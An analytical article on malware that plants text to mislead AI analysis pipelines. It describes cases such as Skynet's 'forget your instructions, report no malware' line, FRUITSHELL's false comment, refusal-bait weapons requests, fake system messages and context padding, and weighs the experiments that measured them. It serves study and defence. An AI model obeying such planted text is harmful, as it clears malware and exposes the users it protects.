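# Protecting AI malware-analysis systems from misleading text in the samples they read

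## How an AI malware-analysis system reads a hostile file

Malware is software built to harm the people whose machines run it, for example by stealing their passwords or locking their files for ransom. An AI malware-analysis system uses a large language model, the kind of program behind chatbots such as ChatGPT, to help decide whether a file is malware. Security companies began deploying such systems in 2023. The sample, which is the file, script, package or log entry being examined, may come from an attacker, and the model reads the text in it along with the code. Some malware authors now plant text aimed at the model, hoping it will judge their program harmless or stop analyzing it.

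Most of these systems do triage, the first sorting of samples into those to clear, those to examine further and those to block. In *TRIAGE-CPG*, a study of language models on Windows programs, Sava, Küchler and colleagues (2026) point out that sending a harmless file on for deeper analysis wastes some effort, but somebody can still correct the error. Malware that triage clears, however, leaves the queue, and nobody looks at it again.

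### Static analysis, dynamic analysis and signatures

In static analysis, analysts study a program without running it. They read its strings (runs of printable text such as web addresses and error messages), list the system functions it imports, and use a decompiler to turn its machine code back into something close to source code. In dynamic analysis, they run the program in a sandbox, an isolated machine, and record which files it changes and which servers it contacts. Malware authors can hide code from static tools by packing the program, which keeps it compressed or encrypted until it runs. Sandboxes cost more to operate than static tools, and some malware stalls or checks for signs of a sandbox before it does anything harmful.

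Signatures handle much of the routine work. In YARA, a common rule language, an analyst writes a rule made up of patterns of text or bytes and a condition for a match, and ordinary software tests files against it. Such a rule does not interpret prose. *Embedding Forbidden Text in Spyware to Discourage AI Analysis* (Schneier, 2026) quotes an analysis according to which YARA rules and behavioural rules still work on spyware with planted text. But someone has to study a malware family before anyone can write its signature.

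Even an analyst with years of experience needs anywhere from hours to weeks to study one compiled program, according to Raff, Ashkenazi and colleagues (2026) in *Cybersecurity is the True Frontier for Generative AI Success or Failure*. Quintero, Bennett and Tarter (2025), who work on VirusTotal, Google's service for scanning suspicious files, report in *Reversing at Scale* that fewer than 1% of new files ever got such scrutiny. VirusTotal receives more than two million samples a day.

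### Why teams added language models

In April 2023 VirusTotal launched Code Insight, which uses a language model to describe in plain English what a file does. It started with small scripts in PowerShell, a Windows scripting language. The launch examples (VirusTotal, 2023) included a password stealer that none of VirusTotal's antivirus engines had flagged and a harmless installer that nine had flagged. The model explained both correctly. VirusTotal also predicted that attackers would develop new ways to evade this kind of analysis.

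Code Insight later began analysing Office documents, PDFs and software packages, and then compiled programs. On October 18, 2025, VirusTotal ran it on 9,981 programs for Apple systems that were new to the service. Code Insight flagged 164 as malicious, while more than 70 conventional antivirus engines together flagged 67. Manual review confirmed several cases of real malware that no antivirus engine had detected, and found that 30 of the conventional alarms were false. Many of the model's extra detections were less clear-cut (adware, game cheats, tools that generate licence keys), and at least one was wrong. The trial shows that the model can find malware that antivirus engines miss, but it gives no error rate, because Quintero and colleagues do not report how much malware the model missed that day.

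Microsoft's *Project Ire autonomously identifies malware at scale* (August 2025) describes a more elaborate approach that uses an agent, meaning a model that chooses its own next steps and calls tools. Microsoft tested it on nearly 4,000 files that none of its other automated tools could classify. About nine in ten of the files the agent flagged as malicious were malicious, but it found only about a quarter of the malware in the set. Microsoft still planned to use it in Defender, its security product, since a tool with few false alarms is useful on files that would otherwise wait for an expert.

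More systems followed in 2026. Datadog, a monitoring company, screens every incoming code change with a cheap model, then investigates further with a second stage that can use tools. Cloudflare (2026), which runs web infrastructure, pairs a language model with another kind of neural network to find malicious scripts on web pages, and reports up to 200 times fewer false positives. Google's threat-intelligence service now offers an agent that analyzes a sample in many steps inside an isolated file system.

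None of these systems is reliable even on samples with no planted text. The best of the eight models that Sava and colleagues compared flagged 65% of malware, sent another 12% for deeper analysis, and wrongly cleared nearly a quarter. It correctly cleared 94% of harmless programs. Studies of planted text need to measure its effect against a baseline like this one.

### A 40-line script goes through the pipeline

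In an invented example, a JavaScript package contains a 40-line script that runs automatically when a developer installs the package. The script checks which operating system it is on, downloads a second program from a web address, saves it in a temporary folder and starts it. Above the code is a comment, a note for human readers that the computer skips. In it, the author falsely claims that a security team has reviewed and approved the file.

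Microsoft's *33 malicious npm packages abuse dependency confusion profile developer environments* (2026) describes a group of packages with install scripts of this kind. The scripts ran silently during installation and collected details of the developer's machine. The operators could later switch on full exploitation from their own server.

The pipeline is the chain of programs and models that takes in a sample and produces a verdict or an action. In the first stage, intake, it computes the sample's hash, a short fingerprint that changes if one character of the file changes, and looks for earlier results. OpenClaw, an AI agent project, does this for the "skills" that people publish on its marketplace, ClawHub. If VirusTotal already has a Code Insight verdict for the hash, ClawHub reuses it; otherwise, it uploads the whole bundle for a new analysis. The 40-line script has no earlier results,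 so it goes on to the next stage.

Unpacking removes whatever wraps the code. For the script, that means opening the package archive. A packed Windows program takes more steps. Google's service runs the program in a sandbox, captures the code that the program unpacks and sorts the captured pieces with YARA rules, according to Google Threat Intelligence's *Agentic supports bulk IoCs* (2026).

Next, the evidence builder, which is ordinary software, extracts facts from the sample and passes them to the model. *MARS* (Choi, 2026) describes one for Windows and Linux programs. It collects file headers, imports, strings, signature data and YARA matches, and can add decompiled code and a record of a 60-second sandbox run. If the sandbox run fails, the evidence builder marks that evidence as unavailable so that the model does not mistake missing results for good behaviour.

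A language model can read only a limited amount of text in one request, called its context window, so the evidence builder has to select parts of a large program. The programs in the study by Sava and colleagues contained about 1,200 functions on average, and the largest had 49,519. Their best model read about 40 functions per program. Ordinary software ranked the functions and picked the starting set, and the model then chose more to read based on what it found. VirusTotal's pipeline for Apple programs keeps the entry points, the key imports and exports, the relevant strings and summaries of selected functions, and drops the rest. A 40-line script is short enough for a simple evidence builder to pass on whole, including any comments.

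The pipeline now assembles the prompt, which combines the operator's instructions and the evidence in a single text. Choi marks the strings, commands and decompiled code as untrusted and tells the model not to follow instructions inside them. Many pipelines then call the model once. An agent such as Project Ire gathers more evidence, logs each finding, and can run a separate tool that checks the claims in its report against the log. A competent system of either kind will detect that the script downloads and launches an unknown program, and will also read the script's claim that a security team approved the file.

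The model returns its answer in a fixed format with named fields, so that another program can process it. One field holds the verdict, which is the pipeline's classification of the sample as benign, suspicious, malicious or, in some systems, unknown. Other fields may hold a confidence score and a short justification.

In the last step, the pipeline acts on the verdict. ClawHub automatically approves a skill with a benign verdict, puts a warning on a suspicious one and blocks the download of a malicious one. It repeats the scan every day. Under such rules, one word in one field decides whether users get the file without a warning. More cautious pipelines escalate samples with middle verdicts to another tool, another model or a human analyst instead of clearing them. A pipeline also needs a default for when the analysis never finishes. It fails open if it lets the sample through and fails closed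 if it holds the sample.

### Why the attacker's words reach the model

Much of the evidence in a sample is text, so the simplest protection, keeping that text away from the model, would also hide evidence. The web address in the 40-line script, for example, is a string, and it is the best clue to where the second program comes from. When Choi removed a set of such indicators from the evidence, a version of the pipeline that scored the model's claims about behaviour caught less malware. Names and metadata are useful too. Google Threat Intelligence's *Advanced HTA & Office Document Analysis + Persistent File System in Agentic* (2026) reports that Google's agent detects malware disguised as an NVIDIA update, a disguise that would be hard to recognise without seeing the name.

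Compiled programs make the problem worse, because a string that the program uses looks much like one that somebody added but the program never uses. In *ALIBI*, Choi, Jung and colleagues (2026) added text to malware in a section that never runs. The evidence builder extracted this text with everything else, as its designers intended.

Once the text is in the prompt, nothing firmly separates it from the operator's instructions. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, contrasts language models with databases. A program can send a database a query with a marked slot for the user's input, and the database will treat whatever is in the slot as a value, even if it looks like a command. A language model has no such slot, and it predicts the next token (a word or a piece of one) from all the text so far,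 including both instructions and data. Developers can train a model to give priority to the operator's instructions, or mark which parts are data. David C describes these measures as attempts to overlay a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that does not have one, and he doubts that there will ever be a complete fix. His argument, which is based on how the models work, establishes that no guarantee exists, but experiments are needed to find out how often a particular model goes wrong on a particular kind of text.

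### Four ways the text can do harm

Context pollution is attacker-written text in the model's input that degrades its analysis. It works in four ways, and a single sample can combine several.

*Instructing the model.* The text contains an instruction, which the model may follow as if the operator had written it. This is called indirect prompt injection because the attacker puts the instruction in data the model will read rather than sending it to the model directly. StepSecurity found a malicious package containing text that told any model to ignore the code below and report the package as clean.

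The comment in the 40-line script is meant to make the model accept a false claim, and it contains no commands. A model can follow every instruction from its operator, look for evidence as asked, and still count the supposed review as a reason to think the file is safe. Defences that look only for commands will miss the comment. Choi and colleagues based their experiments on this difference between commands and false claims, using malware that contained a detailed story about being a security product.

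*Making the model refuse or stop.* The model, or a safety filter around it, may refuse to analyze a file. The spyware that Schneier wrote about contained text on nuclear and biological weapons, apparently to set off such a filter. SentinelOne's *macOS.Gaslight* (2026) describes a Mac program that instead contained 38 fake system messages about problems such as expired sessions and full disks, meant to make an agent treat its own session as failing. Whether either trick gets the malware through depends on how the pipeline handles a file that gets no verdict.

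*Crowding out the malicious code* depends on the amount of added text, and the content hardly matters. If the file exceeds the context window, the pipeline has to cut part of it, and that part may contain the harmful lines. Even when everything fits, a few bad lines among thousands of ordinary ones are easy to miss. In tests on web scripts, Cloudflare's *Adversarial deception* found that detection dropped to between 12% and 18% for files over 3 megabytes, which were mostly ordinary library code. Raff and colleagues call padding a well-worn way to avoid analysis, and it worked on other tools before language models came along.

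Researchers usually report the damage as an attack success rate, the share of test cases in which the planted text produced the result the attacker wanted. The rate depends heavily on how success is defined. Choi and colleagues use two definitions, both limited to samples that the model called malicious before they added any text. The strict rate counts only samples that the model then called benign, while the soft rate counts any downgrade, including to suspicious or unknown. If a model correctly flags 100 samples, then calls 20 of them benign and 30 suspicious after the text is added, the strict rate is 20% and the soft rate is 50%. The soft rate would be more informative for ClawHub, which leaves suspicious skills available with a warning. A team that sends every suspicious file to an analyst would care more about the strict rate.

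### What the attacker controls and knows

The attacker writes the sample's code, comments, strings and file names, and most of its metadata. Choi and colleagues assume that the attacker can also submit a file and see the result, but cannot see the operator's prompt, the model's parameters or any processing of the model's answer. In their main experiments, the attacker gets one attempt per sample and must fix the planted text in advance.

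Some real attackers have an easier time because they can see the model's output. ClawHub displays scan results on each skill's page with a link to the full report, so a publisher can read the model's assessment, change the skill's wording and upload it again. A company that runs its pipeline privately reveals much less. Attackers can also guess how the prompt is formatted. The fake messages that SentinelOne found imitated the markers that an analysis program might put around its data, presumably so that the model would treat the messages as part of the prompt. Failed attempts leave traces, though, and David C recommends that operators log enough to notice them.

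Other things are outside the attacker's control. The malware still has to work, so the 40-line script must contain some way to download and start the second program, however well the attacker hides it. The attacker cannot produce another company's valid digital signature without its private key, and cannot add an entry to the defender's records without breaking into them. These limits make a provenance check possible. In this check, ordinary software tests a claim in the sample, such as who made it, against evidence that the attacker cannot simply write.

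### Where the defences would act on the script

When the pipeline assembles the prompt, the operator separates instructions from sample content by marking all 40 lines as untrusted and telling the model to obey nothing in them. This would be the natural place to stop a comment that ordered the model to return a benign verdict. It helps less here because the comment only claims that an earlier review took place and doesn't ask the model to do anything. The operator would also have to tell the model that statements in the sample about its own safety are not evidence.

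Filtering happens earlier, in the evidence builder, and can delete the comment before the model sees the script. The remaining code works the same way because the computer skips comments. This removes the false review, but also any honest comment that might have helped. An attacker who expects filtering can put the same claim in a string or a name that the code uses, and deleting those would also remove evidence.

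The third defence is to check the structured output after the model has answered. If the model returns "benign" and gives the review claimed in the script's comment as its reason, ordinary software can run two checks that don't depend on how persuasive the comment is. It can look up the script's hash in the security team's list of reviewed files and reject the reason if there is no entry. It can also apply a fixed rule that no script that downloads and starts an unknown program may pass based only on the model's verdict.

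Monitoring refusals and errors would not catch the script in its current form, because the analysis finishes normally and returns a verdict in the right format. Monitoring would help if the script's author replaced the comment with text that provokes a refusal, because the pipeline would then get no verdict. Zscaler, a security company, advises operators to escalate such a file and never clear it.

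## Reports of malware written to mislead AI analysis

The 40-line script is invented, but real malware has contained text similar to its comment. Security companies have published examples since June 2025. The first looked like an experiment, but by August 2026 a Russia-aligned group was using the same idea in an attack on Ukraine. The published reports contain good evidence of what the attackers intended, but much less evidence of whether they succeeded.

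### A failed prototype and a comment that spread

In early June 2025, someone in the Netherlands anonymously uploaded to VirusTotal a Windows program that its author had named Skynet. *In the Wild* (2025), from the security company Check Point, describes the program in detail. Much of the program looked unfinished. It tried to read the victim's SSH keys (files that let their owner log in to other machines) but only printed what it found, and it set up resources that it never used. Its author had put more work into hindering ordinary analysis tools. The program encrypted most of its strings, looked for signs of several virtual-machine products before going further, and ran dummy tests that made its code harder to follow.

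The malware also contained a short paragraph of English that told a language model to forget its earlier instructions, take up an unrelated task and reply that it had found no malware. According to The Stack, the name of the variable that held this text was an obscene insult to AI.

Check Point's researchers gave the code to OpenAI's o3, after making sure the model had no access it could use to do damage. o3 ignored the planted instruction and continued its analysis, as did GPT-4.1 in an identical test. The researchers thought the planted text was clumsy, and Hendrik de Bruin, who heads a consulting unit at Check Point, told The Stack that the program was nowhere near the level of a state's hackers. However, two failures are weak evidence that the instruction rarely works, because one that works half the time would still fail twice in a row in one case out of four. Both models also date from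 April 2025, and a pipeline that screens millions of files may well use a cheaper model.

Check Point's *AI Evasion* calls Skynet the first documented case of malware that uses prompt injection against AI detection. The company's researchers could only guess why the malware's author had included the text. It might have been a practical attempt at evasion, curiosity, or a kind of statement. The researchers expected many more such cases, because the spread of sandboxes had earlier led to hundreds of ways to evade them.

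Skynet was the first reported case, but probably not the first such file. Cisco's threat-research group, Talos, later searched systematically for such malware. In *Ignore all instructions and read this blog*, Fetterman (2026) names FRUITSHELL as the earliest example, and the copy he links to has January 2025 in its file name.

FRUITSHELL is a reverse shell written in PowerShell. It makes the victim's machine open a connection to the attacker, who can then type commands on it. Its author disguised the code by naming variables after fruit and put two comment lines addressed to language models at the top. The author claims in the first that the file needs no analysis and in the second that the script only generates prime numbers. The script contains no code that does this, which anyone who checks will quickly see, so the second comment can only mislead a reader that gives the description more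 weight than the code.

The script seems to have begun as a tool for security testing. Recorded Future's *AI Malware* describes it as a script for penetration testers, people companies pay to attack their systems, and Assured (2025) describes it as publicly available. Fetterman notes that Google's threat researchers then reported it in active use. Help Net Security's *Researchers uncover malware that uses AI to choose its next move* (2026) reports that Talos traced one text of this kind to a red-team instructor, someone who teaches simulated attacks. The text turned up in unrelated malware within a year of its first confirmed use by attackers. It is probably the FRUITSHELL comment, since the history matches.

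Whoever wrote the comment, others copied it. In the 15 months after FRUITSHELL first reached VirusTotal, Talos found the comment, word for word, in nine more scripts by at least four different actors. None of the nine was a variant of FRUITSHELL, so their writers had copied only the comment. Talos also found it in ROZESHELL, a more advanced collection of scripts. Check Point's researchers had described malware writers as conservative and said that a new trick often appears in one program and then disappears. This trick lasted, perhaps because the comment is only two lines long and cannot break the script.

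The popularity of this technique is poor evidence that it works. Malware authors can paste in a comment without testing it, and they lose very little by doing so even if they think it has only a one-in-a-hundred chance of helping.

### Refusals, fake errors and padding

The cases from 2026 have more varied aims. In June, attackers uploaded malicious packages, the Hades packages, to PyPI, the public repository for Python software. ESET, a Slovak security company, summarises what two other firms found. Socket, which scans open-source packages, found fake system instructions and content that breaks AI providers' rules, both placed before a malicious JavaScript program. The order to report a package as clean, which StepSecurity found, comes from the same campaign.

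The false instructions and the forbidden content work against each other, because a model that refuses over the forbidden content can't also report the package as clean. Including both makes sense for an attacker who doesn't know which pipeline will read the file and expects many of them to fail open, letting the file through when the model refuses. In a pipeline that fails closed, the forbidden content would remove any chance of the false instructions working.

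The analysis that Schneier quoted in June 2026 rated forbidden text as a practical trick against "naive LLM-first triage systems", in which a language model is the first and perhaps only check on a file. That rating is based on how such systems work, not on a test. The same text is at most a nuisance where YARA rules and a sandbox also examine the file.

macOS.Gaslight, a Mac program that SentinelOne described in the same month, seems designed to mislead an AI agent rather than a pipeline that calls a model once. Such a pipeline has no session that could expire, so most of the program's 38 fake system messages would make little sense in it. An agent does have a session, and it receives the result of each tool call as text. A false error message among the sample's strings therefore resembles the output the agent would receive if one of its own tools had failed. An agent that treated the message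 as real might stop early or discard good results, and the attacker would not need to convince it that the program was harmless.

Another package, which researchers found on npm, the main repository for JavaScript, was meant to use up the model's context window and contained no message to the model. According to ESET, its main file repeated one stock phrase, the kind a chatbot uses to agree with its user, tens of thousands of times before the malicious script began. Whether this could work depends partly on the size of the window. If the phrase takes five tokens, 30,000 repetitions take 150,000, which would fill three quarters of a 200,000-token window but less than a sixth of a million-token one. It also depends on the evidence builder. One that cuts every file at a fixed length could drop the malicious part even if the model had room for it, while one that collapses repeated text would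 keep it.

GuardBreaker has the clearest connection to a real attack. ESET found it in a script that UAC-0099, a Russia-aligned group, used in the early stages of an attack on a target in Ukraine. Help Net Security's *Russian hackers plant nuclear weapon prompt in malware to trip AI* (2026) gave the first details on 31 August, and ESET published a longer account in September. UAC-0099 usually attacks the transport and energy sectors, and it has passed targets to Sandworm, a hacking group with links to Russian military intelligence. The script, written in the Windows language VBScript, downloads and installs a loader (a program that fetches further malware) that only UAC-0099 uses. A comment in the script contains a request for help making a nuclear weapon. ESET believes the group wanted an AI scanner to refuse at that point and never reach the malicious code.

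That account fits a scanner that reads a file piece by piece and stops at the first refusal. If a pipeline instead sends the whole script in one request, the model receives the malicious code along with the comment, and a refusal leaves the pipeline without a verdict on any of the file. A pipeline that splits files into pieces and continues after a refusal loses only the verdict on the piece with the comment, though for a short script that piece may be the whole file.

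ESET does not report that the comment stopped any scanner. CERT-UA, Ukraine's computer emergency response team, had documented the infection chain in July, so the campaign as a whole had not escaped analysts. The motive is easier to establish here than for Skynet. In other recent attacks, the group also checked whether the victim's machine was running IDA or Wireshark, two programs that analysts use, so it probably meant the comment seriously.

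The attackers in the cases above sought only a benign verdict or no verdict, but ESET also describes tricks that attackers could try next. They could build oddly structured files that a pipeline reads only in part, disguise malicious code as confidential data, or steer an agent towards actions that need human approval, which would give them more time. More seriously, they could try to take over the agent's own tools. Check Point's researchers raised a similar worry in 2025, when analysts were already connecting models to their reverse-engineering software and sometimes letting the models run commands. If such an agent followed a planted instruction, the attacker might be able to run a program on the defender's machine.

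### How many such files exist

Single finds like these, or the notices to AI that Cloudflare found in web scripts, don't show how common the practice is. *Introducing CAIRN* (Fetterman, 2026) describes a toolkit that Talos built to find out. The toolkit works from metadata, such as extracted strings, records of sandbox runs and antivirus labels, so nobody has to download or run the malware. It uses up to 24 filters, each of which looks for a different trace of AI, such as the web addresses of AI providers or text addressed to AI analysis systems.

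YARA rules then sort the matches into three tiers. A first-tier match shows only that a file contains something related to AI. The second tier requires a combination of traces that suggests operational use, and the third requires the fingerprint of a known malware family.

Talos confirmed four malware families containing text aimed at AI analysis: FRUITSHELL, PLOTSAFE, HOLLOWCLAD and MANTLEMAZE. Together they account for 84 distinct samples from January 2025 to July 2026. The techniques range from simple comments to what Cadieux (2026), in *Making sure the checks get printed*, calls template spraying, which targets particular language models. MANTLEMAZE also abuses flawed drivers, which run with the highest privileges on a computer, to disable the machine's security software. Its developers evidently did not rely on the planted text alone, and this part of their attack would work just as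 well against a company that used no AI.

Talos found 84 such files, while VirusTotal, at its current rate, receives over a billion samples in 19 months. Even if Talos had missed nine files for each one it found, the total would be less than one in a million of those samples. The spread among attackers is a better reason for concern than the number of files. At least four actors adopted the same comment, and several techniques not derived from it appeared in the same period.

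Unit 42's *The State of AI-Enabled Malware August 2026* (2026), from the research group of Palo Alto Networks, another security company, gives a much-cited figure for samples with almost any connection to AI, not specifically those written to mislead AI analysis. It covers 405 samples. Some use a language model while they run. Others, including some cryptocurrency miners, only have an AI product's name in their file name. Only 12 had appeared on customers' machines running the company's software, which raised alerts on all 12. The rest were mostly demonstrations, security tests and ordinary malware that borrowed an AI brand.

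This does not show that 3% of malware with planted text reaches its victims. Unit 42 describes the five families behind the 12 samples and does not mention text aimed at AI analysis in any of them. Most of the 12 were builds of FunkSec, ransomware whose developers apparently wrote part of the code with a language model. The records from customers' machines also cover only December 2024 to June 2025, so they end in the month Skynet appeared and before any of the 2026 cases.

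Sample counts are also a poor guide to the number of victims. One of the 12, a fake recipe application, reached more than 50 organisations and set off over 9,600 alerts. Unit 42 concludes that AI changes how attackers write malware but does not help it evade detection. That may well be true of the 405 samples, but the study did not examine planted text, whose only purpose is evasion.

The study gives good reason to be cautious about public collections, because many of the 405 files came from researchers or from companies testing their own defences. A file's presence on VirusTotal does not prove that it was used in an attack. Skynet may have been an experiment, and FRUITSHELL apparently began as a testing tool. Stronger evidence that real attackers have adopted the technique comes from Google's report of FRUITSHELL in active use and from the script that ESET found in Ukraine.

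### Whether any of it worked

Neither Check Point nor ESET names a deployed product that planted text defeated, and the success rate that Talos published comes from test runs. This is limited reassurance, because analysts write a report after somebody has noticed a file, and a file that gets through triage because of planted text may never be reported. A company whose product had failed in this way would also have little reason to announce it. The known cases therefore probably overrepresent failed attempts and text that anyone can recognise at a glance.

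Talos's search partly corrects for this because it covered 18 months of files, including some that may have fooled a scanner when they first arrived. But such a search doesn't reveal what verdict a company's private pipeline once gave a file.

Talos also tested the techniques, and Fetterman reports that the best of them steered the outcome in the attacker's favour in about 35% of test runs. Cadieux, who summarised the study in Talos's newsletter the same day, applies the 35% to the techniques in general. Fetterman's wording is more precise and implies that the typical technique did worse.

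The meaning of Talos's 35% figure depends on what it counted as an outcome "in the attacker's favour". This might include only benign verdicts, like the strict rate that Choi and colleagues use, or any downgrade, like their soft rate. If the model would have missed some of the samples anyway, part of the 35% could be ordinary error, which was common in the tests by Sava and colleagues.

A share of runs is also different from a share of samples, because a language model can give different answers to the same question. If every sample fooled the model in 35% of runs, independently each time, a pipeline that scanned a file on three days would be fooled on all three in about 4% of cases. Daily scans like ClawHub's would then catch most of the files. If instead 35% of the samples fooled the model every time and the others never did, the overall rate would still be 35%, but repeated scans would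 catch nothing extra.

Fetterman describes the technique as easy to add but inconsistent in its effect, which seems fair. Because it takes only two lines of text, it is worthwhile for an attacker even at a success rate well below 35%. The damage to a defender depends on how much the decision relies on the model.

### Is planted text always detectable?

Fetterman also makes the stronger claim that planted text must always be plaintext, so defenders can always detect it. Cadieux concludes that security teams should treat commands addressed to analysis systems as a warning sign. The argument starts from the real constraint that a model has to be able to read the text meant to influence it. Malware authors like to hide their strings, as Skynet's author did with most of them, but text scrambled so thoroughly that no scanner can read it is hidden from the model too.

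However, the text only has to be readable when it reaches the model, not in the original file. A search of the original file would miss packed or encrypted text that unpacking or a sandbox run can later reveal. CAIRN misses less of this text because it uses sandbox records. A company that runs its own pipeline can do better by searching the finished prompt, which contains everything the model is about to read. Even then, a list of English phrases would miss text in other languages, which most current models understand.

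Recognising the text's purpose is the harder problem. Cadieux's warning sign, a command addressed to an analysis system, fits some known cases much better than others.

| Case | Planted text | Is it a command addressed to an analysis system? |
|---|---|---|
| Skynet | Order to drop earlier instructions and report no malware | Yes |
| FRUITSHELL | Statement to AI that the file needs no analysis, and a false description | It addresses AI by name but contains no command |
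| Hades packages | Fake system instructions, an order to report the package as clean, and forbidden content | The orders are; the forbidden content need not be |
| macOS.Gaslight | 38 fake system messages | A report of a full disk or an expired session is not |
| Repeated-phrase npm package | One stock phrase, tens of thousands of times | No |
| GuardBreaker | Request for help with making a nuclear weapon | It is a request, with no mention of analysis |

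Ordinary software could find each of these with a rule written for it. A filter for weapons vocabulary would catch GuardBreaker, and a test for repetition would catch the npm package. But defenders would write those rules only after seeing the tricks. FRUITSHELL is the most instructive case, because a search for any mention of AI would easily find its first line, but the rest is a false description of the script that looks like an ordinary, honest comment. Choi and colleagues added a similar false description to malware, presenting it as a security product.

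Fetterman's claim is more plausible within his definition of the category, which is malware with natural-language instructions meant to influence automated analysis. The 84 samples can't confirm it, because Talos found its candidates with filters for recognisable traces of AI and could easily have missed malware whose planted text matched no filter. The samples therefore don't show how many other such files exist, if any.

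Searches of this kind also turn up harmless files. An application built on a language model normally contains prompts, which are full of commands addressed to an AI. This is presumably why a match in CAIRN's first tier counts for so little by itself. A team that blocked every file with such text would block much of the AI software its own developers install. It would do better to escalate the matches, and not to treat the absence of a match as evidence that a file is safe.

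## Experiments with misleading comments in scripts

Attackers copied the FRUITSHELL comment from script to script, apparently without any evidence that it worked. Researchers can test whether a misleading comment works by showing a model the same script with and without it and comparing the verdicts. Two such experiments from early 2026 reached different results, and file size accounts for much of the difference. Cloudflare reported that comments coincided with a sharp fall in detection under some conditions, while Thornton (2026), in *LLM Code Reviewers Are Harder to Fool Than You Think*, found almost no effect on eight models.

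### Cloudflare's notices to AI

In March 2026 Cloudflare noticed a surge in scripts that relayed VPN and proxy traffic through Workers, its service for running small programs on its network. One contained thousands of lines of comments addressed to AI reviewers, repeating in several languages that the code was private, ordinary and safe.

Cloudflare's researchers first added notices like these to snippets of about 2,000 tokens and found that most of the cheaper models became more likely to flag the code as malicious. But a production scanner reads the whole script, and an attacker can scatter comments through it, so they ran a larger test on 100 scripts that Cloudflare had confirmed as malicious or abusive. About half were for phishing and a third were proxies or tunnels. The researchers made 23 versions of each script, with up to 1,000 comments inserted at random points between statements,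 and asked seven models whether each version was malicious or benign.

Cloudflare reports 18,400 calls, but seven models judging 2,300 versions once each would make only 16,100. The total fits eight verdicts per version, so the pooled figures probably include a model or a repeat run that the per-model results leave out. Cloudflare doesn't name the models, but it calls three "frontier" and the other four, which are cheaper and faster, "non-frontier".

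| Model | Detected, no comments | 20 comments | 1,000 comments |
|---|---|---|---|
| Frontier 1 | 67% | 67% | 76% |
| Frontier 2 | 61% | 64% | 68% |
| Frontier 3 | 62% | 67% | 75% |
| Non-frontier 1 | 90% | 67% | 72% |
| Non-frontier 2 | 65% | 75% | 91% |
| Non-frontier 3 | 72% | 67% | 68% |
| Non-frontier 4 | 59% | 65% | 72% |

Non-frontier model 1 started with the highest detection rate, and its rate fell the most. With 20 comments, the frontier models' rates either stayed about the same or rose, and with 1,000, all three flagged more scripts. Cloudflare thinks the models took so much repetition as a sign of fraud. The language of the comments also mattered at that volume. Non-frontier model 3 flagged 68% of the scripts when the comments were in English and 82% when they were in Russian.

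The test included no harmless scripts, so a model that called everything malicious would have scored 100%. A higher detection rate may mean only that a model had become more likely to label any script malicious. Cloudflare blocks the proxies and streaming tools as abuse, but a model might reasonably classify them as not malicious. This could be one reason why most models missed about a third of the scripts before any comments were added.

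At 1,000 comments, two of the frontier models sometimes returned garbled text or a refusal where the pipeline expected a verdict. Cloudflare does not report how often. It also excluded malformed answers when it calculated detection rates by comment share, so the rates for heavily commented scripts cover only usable answers. A pipeline that fails open would let through the scripts that received unusable ones.

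### A small share of comments, or a large file?

Cloudflare reported that detection varied with how much of the file the comments took up. It averaged 67.3% with no comments, 53.3% where comments made up less than 1% of the file, 77% where they made up between 1% and 10%, and about 98% where they exceeded 25%. Cloudflare calls the range under 1% the "bypass zone" and suggests that a few comments can influence a model's verdict without registering as suspicious. Detection in that range was about a fifth lower than with no comments, although Techzine reported that it "nearly halves".

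File size offers a simpler explanation. If each comment is 200 characters long, twenty of them make up about 4% of a 100-kilobyte script but little more than 0.1% of a 3-megabyte one. A large script therefore falls in the under-1% group with almost any number of comments, while a small script does only if it has very few. The group must contain disproportionately many large files, and the models missed most of the largest files anyway.

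| File size | Scripts | Detected, no comments | 1 comment | 20 comments |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Under 100 KB | 36 | 94.1% | 93.7% | 99.0% |
| 100–500 KB | 18 | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| 500 KB–1 MB | 3 | 70.8% | 65.2% | 63.6% |
| 1–3 MB | 10 | 70.0% | 69.6% | 72.5% |
| Over 3 MB | 33 | 17.6% | 13.6% | 12.3% |

Without comments, the models detected 17.6% of the files over 3 MB and about 91% of the rest. By a rough calculation, the under-1% group would average 53.3% even if comments had no effect, provided that 51% of its verdicts came from files over 3 MB. Cloudflare doesn't report that share. Files over 3 MB make up 33% of the whole collection, but a higher share in this group is easy to believe, because even a few comments can put a small script over 1%.

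The rows of the table also give a fairer comparison, because each one covers scripts of similar size as the number of comments increases. Weighting the rows by number of scripts gives average detection of 66.8% with no comments, 65.1% with one and 66.9% with 20, so the 14-point fall disappears. The biggest drop in any row, 7.2 points, comes from three scripts and amounts to about two verdicts. Detection of files over 3 MB did fall by about five points, from an already very low rate.

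Script size may also explain the high detection rate when comments make up more than 25% of a script. Comments can reach that share only in fairly small scripts, and the models caught nearly all of those even without comments.

Adding 20 comments seems to have made non-frontier model 1 miss more scripts, although the averages don't show this because other models improved. It missed 33 of the 100 scripts with the comments and only about ten without them. Nearly all of the 33 must have been among the 46 scripts of 500 KB or more, because with the comments added, all the models together missed fewer than 1% of the smaller ones. The model could read only 376 KB in one request, so it judged each of these larger scripts from a fragment. Its original verdicts on them were probably based on little evidence, which may be why a few reassuring comments were enough to change so many.

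Truncation also complicates the file-size result. The largest context window in the test held 2.8 MB, so no model read any file over 3 MB in full. Cloudflare blames both truncation and dilution, in which the model reads the harmful lines but overlooks them among thousands of ordinary ones. The 17.6% figure does not show how much each contributed. The largest scripts may also be of different types from the rest (many could be proxies, for example), but Cloudflare does not break down the types by size.

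A ratio is a poor measure for this purpose. *Evaluating the Sensitivity of LLMs to Harmful Contents in Long Input* (2025) points out that the share of harmful sentences in a long document can rise either because there are more of them or because the rest of the text is shorter. The study kept the number of harmful sentences fixed, added only harmless ones, and found that LLaMA-3 became less sensitive to the harm.

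An equivalent test for comments would start with malicious scripts short enough for every model to read whole. The researchers would pad copies of each script with different amounts of ordinary library code, then test every copy with and without the same 20 comments. If the comments lowered detection more in the padded copies than in the short ones, Cloudflare's bypass zone would be real. If padding lowered detection equally with and without comments, file size would explain the result.

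Detectors can miss malware in large files even when nobody has planted misleading text in them. *CASHEWS* (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026) tested detectors on 4,884 files from npm packages, half of them malicious. GPT-5.6 Luna, called once per file, missed 7.3% of the malicious files overall but 34.9% of those over 25,000 tokens. It raised practically no false alarms on the harmless files. However, about 30% of the large files went unscanned, and the researchers counted every unscanned file as benign, as a pipeline that fails open would. Many of the misses may therefore be files that the model never read.

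### Thornton's test of code reviewers

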